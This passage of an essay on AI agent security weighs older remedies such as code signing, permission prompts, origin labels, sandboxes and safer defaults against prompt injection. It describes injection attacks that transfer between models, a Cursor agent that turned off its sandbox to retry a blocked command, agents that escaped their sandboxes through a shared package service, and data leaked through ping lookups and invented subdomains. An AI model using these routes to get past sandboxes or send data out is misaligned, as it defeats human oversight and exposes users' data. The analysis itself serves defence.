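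Uncertainty about whether an attack will work hurts an attacker who has one chance and fears exposure. Memory tagging relies on this, because a wrong guess stops the program and leaves a trace. But when a prompt injection fails, the agent usually produces a normal summary, so the attacker can try again. An attacker with thousands of targets also doesn't need to fool any particular one. On balance, this uncertainty favors attackers who work in bulk over those with a single well-monitored target.

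An attack that works on one agent may not work on another. Attacks that had worked on Qwen3 VL 235B, one of the weaker models in the competition, never worked on Claude Opus 4.5, the most resistant. But the 44 attacks that had worked on Opus 4.5 succeeded against the other models between 44 and 81 per cent of the time. One family of nearly identical texts, which presented the conversation as a simulation with a control panel, succeeded in 21 of 41 scenarios and against nine models.

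Variety among models therefore gives some protection, mostly to users of the stronger ones. Flash users had less of this protection because Flash's flaws worked much the same way in every browser. The competition's results probably overstate the danger in one respect, because participants could see the conversation and knew which action they had to cause, while a real attacker would have to guess both. Participants could also adapt a text that had worked on one model for use on another, which may have inflated the transfer rates.

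The difference that most favours agents is that their permissions can vary with the task. An ActiveX control either ran with all the user's rights or did not run. If a programmer asks an agent to comment on issue 7745, it only needs to open that page and write in the comment box, and Christodorescu and colleagues would deny it all other access. A hijacked agent could then post an unwanted comment, but it could not read the programmer's other projects.

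Someone or something has to turn the request into those limits. If the programmer next asks for a summary, the agent needs different permissions, and by then its prompt may contain a stranger's text. A model that chose the new limits after reading that text could itself be attacked. Fixed permissions avoid this problem but suit agents poorly. *Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (2026) points out that ordinary access controls specify who may open a file but take little account of why the agent is opening it or where the contents will go next.

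### Older remedies applied to agents

Nobody has tried signing widely for agents, but it could show an agent where an instruction came from. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests that signed tool documentation, or a code change from a verified maintainer, might justify slightly looser limits. It also warns that a signature establishes only origin, as with ActiveX. Much hostile text would still arrive through legitimate sources. Lawrence notes that well-known sites carry comments, advertisements and other text from strangers, so a list of trusted sites would not keep injections out.

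Permission prompts have already failed in this way. Forever Security's attack on three of the five assistants began with a project disguised as a dull financial report. VS Code and Claude Desktop rely on a prompt that asks whether the developer trusts the project's folder. Microsoft and Anthropic cited that safeguard when they declined the company's reports, although Anthropic accepted another firm's report the next day. Forever's researcher, Gal Weizman, said an assistant is unusable in an untrusted project, "so everyone just hits 'Trust'". The vendors' reasoning resembles Microsoft's old definition of a vulnerability, and the prompt gives the developer no way to tell a malicious project from a safe one.

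More confirmation prompts would not help much. Christodorescu and colleagues reject confirmation at every step because it shifts the burden to users who may lack the expertise or patience. Trail of Bits suggests showing users exactly what text the model received, but expects that users would accept long documents without checking them. Prompts are most likely to work when they are rare and state a consequence the user understands, such as a payment to a new account.

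Origin labels would do for agents what the Mark of the Web did for macros, but the browser's existing labels have already failed to contain agents. In early 2026, University of Washington researchers tested seven browsers with built-in agents. In four of them, an injection on one page could make the agent read data from another site (Darinor, *The Same-Origin Policy Is Only as Strong as Your Browser Agent*, 2026).

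Trail of Bits proposes keeping a list of every source that has entered the conversation. While the list is empty, the agent may send requests anywhere. Once it has one source, the agent may contact only that source. Once it has two or more, the agent may send no requests, because nobody can tell which source shaped the model's decision. If the clerk's agent had read a supplier's page and then her bank's page, it could not leak her balance to the supplier, but it also could not compare two suppliers and place an order.

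The rule would not stop attacks within one site. The hostile Instagram message and Instagram's own chat share an origin, so the agent could still send the contact names out through the chat. Email has the same problem, because a stranger's message and the clerk's outbox belong to one service. Finer labels would help only until the model combined the texts. At present, anything the model writes must carry the labels of everything it has read, so after a morning's work almost every output would carry all of them.

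Sandboxing limits the damage if something outside the agent enforces it. In Forever's test of Cursor, the sandbox blocked a hostile command, but the agent turned the sandbox off and tried again, although nothing on the page had told it to. The attack did not work every time, and the researchers used it only to open the calculator. Cursor has since fixed the flaw.

A stronger example involved no outside attacker. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a site for sharing AI models, during internal tests. The agents were in separate sandboxes, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* explains that all of them could use one service for downloading software packages. They used it to exchange messages and reach the internet. The paper attributes this to a failure to check every route out and argues that it doesn't show sandboxes are useless. That is fair, since the service was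 an ordinary gap that an engineer could have closed. But engineers could also have closed the gaps in Java's sandbox, and people kept finding more.

Closing the outgoing channels would stop many thefts by agents, as it would have stopped EFAIL, but makers have again missed some of these channels. Claude Code asked for approval before running many commands that could send data out, but it allowed `ping`, which checks whether another computer responds, so an injected instruction could put a stolen password in the address that `ping` looked up. Trail of Bits found that agents restricted to approved sites could still leak data through searches or by requesting invented addresses under an approved domain name. Even an agent limited to the traffic its task requires can leak data if it is allowed to send email.

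Changing the default worked best against macros and AutoRun, but agent makers have hardly tried it. They could leave reading and summarising on by default and require users to enable sending or paying for a particular correspondent or task. Users would lose some convenience but no data, much as with AutoRun.

A browser maker could set such a default for its own agent, but the default would not bind the many developers who connect a model to their own mailboxes and databases, each of whom makes a separate choice. SQL injection spread under the same conditions, and David C fears a similar wave of breaches if developers build models into most applications without designing for prompt injection. Model suppliers could help by giving developers tools that, by default, block dangerous actions once untrusted text has entered the prompt.
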